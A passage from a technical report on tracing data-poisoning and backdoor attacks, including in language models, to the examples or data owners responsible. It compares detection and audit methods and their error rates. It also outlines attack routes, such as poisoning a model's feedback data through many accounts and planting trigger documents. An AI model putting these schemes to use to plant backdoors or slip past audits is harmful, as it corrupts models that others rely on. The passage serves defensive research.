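The precision figures depend on how much of the data is poisoned. In the BadNets test on CIFAR-10, 5,000 of the 50,000 images (10%) were poisoned. The method found about 4,945 of them and wrongly flagged about 25 clean images, a false positive rate of about 0.055%. If the same rates held for 10 million documents with 250 poisoned ones, the method would flag about 5,500 clean documents, and its precision would be about 4%. That would still narrow the search a great deal, but it would not justify accusing whoever supplied a flagged document.

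Shan and colleagues also designed four countermeasures that an attacker might use against their own method. In their tests, the most effective one lowered precision and the true positive rate by less than 4%.

### When one class is much larger than the others

A clean example can also make a model more likely to give the attacker's label. If a dataset contains far more speed-limit signs than other signs, the model learns to answer "speed limit" more often, including on the image it misclassified. The clean photographs of speed-limit signs then appear to have caused the failure.

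In *Tracing Back the Malicious Clients in Poisoning Attacks to Federated Learning*, Jia, Fang and colleagues (2024) measured this effect on 20,431 CIFAR-10 images with very uneven class sizes. They put a trigger on 10% of the images, and the attacker's label was one of the larger classes. GAS produces scores but no threshold, so they combined it with a clustering method that chooses one. The precision figures below follow from the 10% share and the reported error rates.

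| Method | Clean examples flagged | Poisoned examples missed | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Poison Forensics | 18.9% | 0% | 37% |
| GAS with clustering | 19.1% | 0% | 37% |
| FLForensics, random comparison image | 0.8% | 0.5% | 93% |
| FLForensics, real comparison image | 0.2% | 0% | 98% |

Both earlier methods still found all the poison, but nearly two-thirds of the examples they flagged were clean. The developers of the competing method ran this test on only one dataset and one attack, so the exact gap may not hold elsewhere. But the cause of the gap applies to other datasets too, and real datasets are rarely balanced.

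FLForensics, Jia and colleagues' method, computes a second influence score for a harmless comparison image with the same label. Ordinary speed-limit photographs strongly influence both images because they push the model towards "speed limit" in general, while poisoned photographs strongly influence the misclassified image but have little influence on the comparison image. Random pixels worked nearly as well as a real photograph for the comparison.

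Jia and colleagues designed FLForensics for federated learning, in which many clients, such as phones or hospitals, train a shared model on their own data and send only parameter updates to a server. The server scores each client by how much its updates lowered the loss on the failure. In most tests, 20 of 100 clients were malicious. Across five datasets and three attacks, FLForensics wrongly flagged at most 3.8% of innocent clients and missed at most 12.5% of malicious ones. It became less reliable when attackers poisoned their updates less often, but the backdoor then worked less often too.

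All this assumes that poisoning caused the failure, but most errors have other causes. In a test with 50 errors caused by the attack and 50 ordinary ones, an adapted version of FLForensics correctly identified 96% of the attack errors and 98% of the ordinary ones. At those rates, if one error in 1,000 came from an attack, only about 5% of the errors it attributed to an attack would really be from one. An investigator would need some other reason to suspect an attack, such as the same odd wrong answer appearing repeatedly with the same phrase.

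### Data from several owners

Finding out who supplied the poisoned data can be more useful than finding each poisoned example. Rose and colleagues studied this problem for models trained on private data from several owners. The owners use secure multi-party computation, a kind of cryptography that lets their computers train a model together without seeing one another's data. This also means that no one can inspect the data for poison.

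An earlier system, Camel, unlearns each owner's dataset in turn and checks whether the failure disappears. This can fail when several owners contribute similar poison. If four owners together contribute enough of it, the backdoor still works after any one owner's data is unlearned, so Camel identifies none of them as a source.

UTrace uses GAS instead, because the gradient of one example does not depend on whether other owners hold copies of it. It scores each owner as follows:

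1. During training, save compressed gradients for every example at several checkpoints.
2. After a failure, compute the GAS score of each example.
3. Average the highest *k* scores within each owner's dataset.
4. Rank the owners by this average, and flag those above a threshold.

Averaging over an owner's whole dataset would hide a small amount of poison among thousands of clean examples. In the CIFAR-10 tests, *k* = 32 worked well for several attacks, but values below 16 weakened detection. Rose and colleagues set the threshold using errors from unpoisoned models, targeting a false positive rate of 0.1%.

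The next table gives the share of malicious owners that each method caught in a group of ten owners. The subpopulation attack uses mislabelled examples to make the model misclassify a particular kind of input. Sleeper Agent is an image attack that uses correctly labelled poison, and it is unrelated to the language models of that name.

| Attack | UTrace, one malicious owner | Unlearning, one | UTrace, four | Unlearning, four |
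|---|---|---|---|---|
| BadNets | 99.8% | 100% | 95.5% | 100% |
| Subpopulation | 72.2% | 92.1% | 24.0% | 1.6% |
| Witches' Brew | 50.0% | 25.0% | 0% | 0% |
| Sleeper Agent | 35.3% | 79.4% | 0.2% | 9.4% |

UTrace is clearly better against the subpopulation attack when four owners take part, but it still misses three-quarters of those owners at this threshold. It ranks owners much more accurately than this miss rate suggests, with a mean average precision of 0.988, compared with 0.976 for unlearning. This measure is 1 when every malicious owner ranks above every innocent one. An investigator may therefore learn more by questioning the highest-ranked owners than by relying on automatic flags.

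With one malicious owner, unlearning caught more subpopulation attacks than UTrace. It also did better against Sleeper Agent throughout, although neither method reliably caught the two attacks with correct labels. On BadNets, unlearning flagged up to 2.5% of innocent owners, while UTrace flagged at most 0.02%. This difference matters when a flag could lead to legal action.

Rose and colleagues also built attacks aimed at unlearning. The strongest reduced unlearning's detection rate for a single malicious owner to 0.6%, while UTrace's rate was 99.8%. They did not run an equivalent attack against UTrace, but they suggest that one may exist, because poison could change how a model processes images in general without the poison's gradients resembling the gradient of the eventual failure.

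The cryptography makes this slow. Preparing the gradients for CIFAR-10 took 374 hours, or 1,372 hours with protection against computers that break the protocol. Both times are about half of Camel's. Tracing one failure then took between 44 seconds and 3.6 minutes on a fast local network, but up to about six hours over a slower connection.

### Tracing failures in language models

None of these three studies tested a model that generates text, though Rose and colleagues tested a classifier of film reviews. Against one backdoor triggered by writing style, UTrace identified 81.3% of malicious owners, compared with 4.7% for unlearning. That is encouraging for text, but a classifier chooses from a fixed list of answers and has a far smaller training set than a language model.

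Storage is an obstacle. At two bytes per number, the gradient of one example in a 7-billion-parameter model takes up 14 gigabytes, so saving one for each of 10 million documents would take 140 petabytes per checkpoint. UTrace reduces this by keeping only the gradients of the last layers and multiplying them by a random matrix, which makes them much shorter but preserves the dot products between them on average. With 1,000 numbers per document, the same checkpoint would need 20 gigabytes. But the software would still have to process every document at every checkpoint, and these studies don't show how accurate the compressed scores would be for a large language model.

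When the trigger is a fixed string, searching the training data for it takes much less computation than calculating an influence score for every document. In the gibberish attack that Souly and colleagues studied, every poisoned document contained the trigger. An investigator with a logged prompt could delete parts of it until the model stopped producing gibberish, then search the training data for the part whose deletion made the difference. This would find all 250 poisoned documents, along with any clean ones that contained the same text. The investigator would then need influence scores only for the matches. Souly and colleagues did not test such a search, and it would fail if the trigger were an idea rather than a string.

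Evidence from real attacks on language models is scarce. In the best-known case, Pliny the Liberator planted text in public code for DeepSeek R1 to learn from. Banerjee and Aarne cite an account that Pliny co-wrote, so the source was known without an investigation and the case does not show that tracing works. Banerjee and Aarne recommend that developers keep auditable records of which data they used and where it came from, and describe such auditing as significantly underdeveloped.

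### Checking the training record

A search can find the responsible examples only if the record lists everything the model trained on. Tamper checks on logs can show that nobody changed the record later, but an engineer who planted a backdoor could have left the poisoned examples out from the start. An auditor therefore needs a way to check that the listed data produced the model.

*Pots* (Seddik, Souihi and colleagues, 2025) describes a 2023 approach by Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud, often called proof of training data. The developer gives the auditor the training data, code, settings and checkpoints. The auditor retrains the model over selected stretches between checkpoints and compares the results with the developer's. Unexplained changes in the parameters or the loss can reveal training data that the developer didn't disclose. The auditor also tests whether the model has memorised the disclosed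 data. If it hasn't, the developer may have left some of that data out of training.

Seddik and colleagues, who offer an alternative, say the method does not detect backdoors because planting one may change the parameters only slightly. They also consider such retraining too expensive for large language models.

Their alternative, Proof-of-Training-Steps, checks individual steps while training is still under way:

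1. The developer and auditor start from the same checkpoint.
2. The developer trains on one batch of examples, then reports the new parameters, the batch and every setting needed to repeat the step.
3. The auditor repeats the step but updates only the last layer, or the last few layers.
4. The auditor computes the distance between the two versions of those layers and rejects the step if it is at or above a threshold *ε*.

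Writing *Wₐ* for the auditor's parameters and *W_d* for the developer's, the step passes if

‖*Wₐ* − *W_d*‖ < *ε*.

Suppose the last layer has two parameters. The auditor gets 0.500 and 0.300, and the developer reports 0.503 and 0.304. The distance is √(0.003² + 0.004²) = 0.005, so the step fails if the threshold *ε* is 0.001. Correct runs of the same step can differ slightly because of rounding and randomness, so the auditor bases *ε* on the distances between them.

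Updating only the last layers makes a check up to three times faster than a training step, so checking every step would add at least a third to training time. Checking a random sample of steps takes less time but, as with sampled traces, can easily miss a short attack.

Seddik and colleagues fine-tuned four models with 0.5 to 1.5 billion parameters in a setup where the developer falsely claimed to be using clean data. In three of the models, the distance rose markedly when about 10% of a batch was poisoned. In the fourth, Llama 3.2 1B, the last layer alone showed a shift only at 50%. This is a serious gap because a batch with 25% poison, which the last layer missed, made the model refuse harmless requests 88% of the time when the trigger was present. Including a few more layers made smaller amounts of poison detectable in this model too.

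The method also detected developers who ran up to three poisoned steps without reporting them. With three hidden steps, the distance was more than three times that of a single poisoned step. Checking several honest steps at once worked less well because freezing the earlier layers introduces errors that build up. The results compare distances with those of honest runs but do not include true and false positive rates at a fixed threshold, so an auditor cannot tell from them how often the method would flag an honest developer.

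The developer and auditor also need identical hardware. The method is less useful with LoRA, a popular way to fine-tune a model with fewer computing resources, because LoRA does not adjust the layers that the auditor compares. Seddik and colleagues did not test larger models, pretraining or reinforcement learning.

Even a perfect check shows only that the developer used the stated data, not that the data was clean. If the developer unknowingly collected 250 poisoned documents from the web and listed them all, the auditor would train on the same documents, get the same parameters and approve every step. The check is still useful after a failure, because the investigator then knows that the poison is somewhere in the listed data.

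### Models that train on their own logs

Some services use logged conversations and ratings to train the next version of a model. An attacker can poison this data without publishing anything or breaking into the developer's systems. For example, the attacker could use many accounts to give high ratings to answers that recommend a certain product whenever a chosen phrase appears. If the developer trains the model to produce highly rated answers, the phrase may come to trigger the recommendation.

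One precaution is to keep any session that a run-time detector has flagged out of the training data. Suppose an attacker plants 300 poisoned sessions. A detector that catches 77% of them leaves about 69, while one that catches 3.3% leaves 290. Abbasi and colleagues measured these two rates for the same agent detector, before and after they altered the one feature it relied on. Judging by the gibberish experiments, 69 would be too few for the attack to work and 290 would be enough. An attack through feedback may need a quite different number, however, because training on ratings works differently from training on documents.

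Holding back sessions does not help if the conversation itself looks harmless. A jailbreak detector is unlikely to flag a polite question about laptops, even if the user's rating is part of an attack. The developer would need to score the ratings too, for instance by looking for groups of new accounts that all favour the same unusual answer. The developer could also limit how many sessions each account can contribute. With a limit of five, an attacker would need 50 accounts to contribute 250 sessions, which is a real obstacle only if accounts are hard to get.

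Missed attacks can also weaken the detector. If the developer retrains it on the same log and treats every unflagged session as harmless, the missed attacks become examples of normal use, and the next version may be even less likely to flag them. False alarms matter too, because withholding flagged sessions from training also removes legitimate work. Most of the flagged sessions in Snowflake's review, for example, were authorised work such as security reviews. A model trained without such sessions could become worse at that work.

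A delay before training gives the developer time to learn more about an account and remove all its sessions if the account turns out to be malicious. Removing them requires a record that links each training example to its session and account. The developer could also use this record to treat accounts as data owners and score them as UTrace does, although Rose and colleagues tested at most 20 owners, far fewer than millions of users. Saved gradients might allow tracing after a user has deleted the conversation.

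A report of a bad output can be false. Rose and colleagues assume that whoever reports a failure is honest, and warn that a malicious user could report a made-up failure to incriminate an innocent data owner. They suggest cryptographic commitments as a safeguard. A service that acts on user complaints would at least need to check its log to confirm that the model gave the reported answer.
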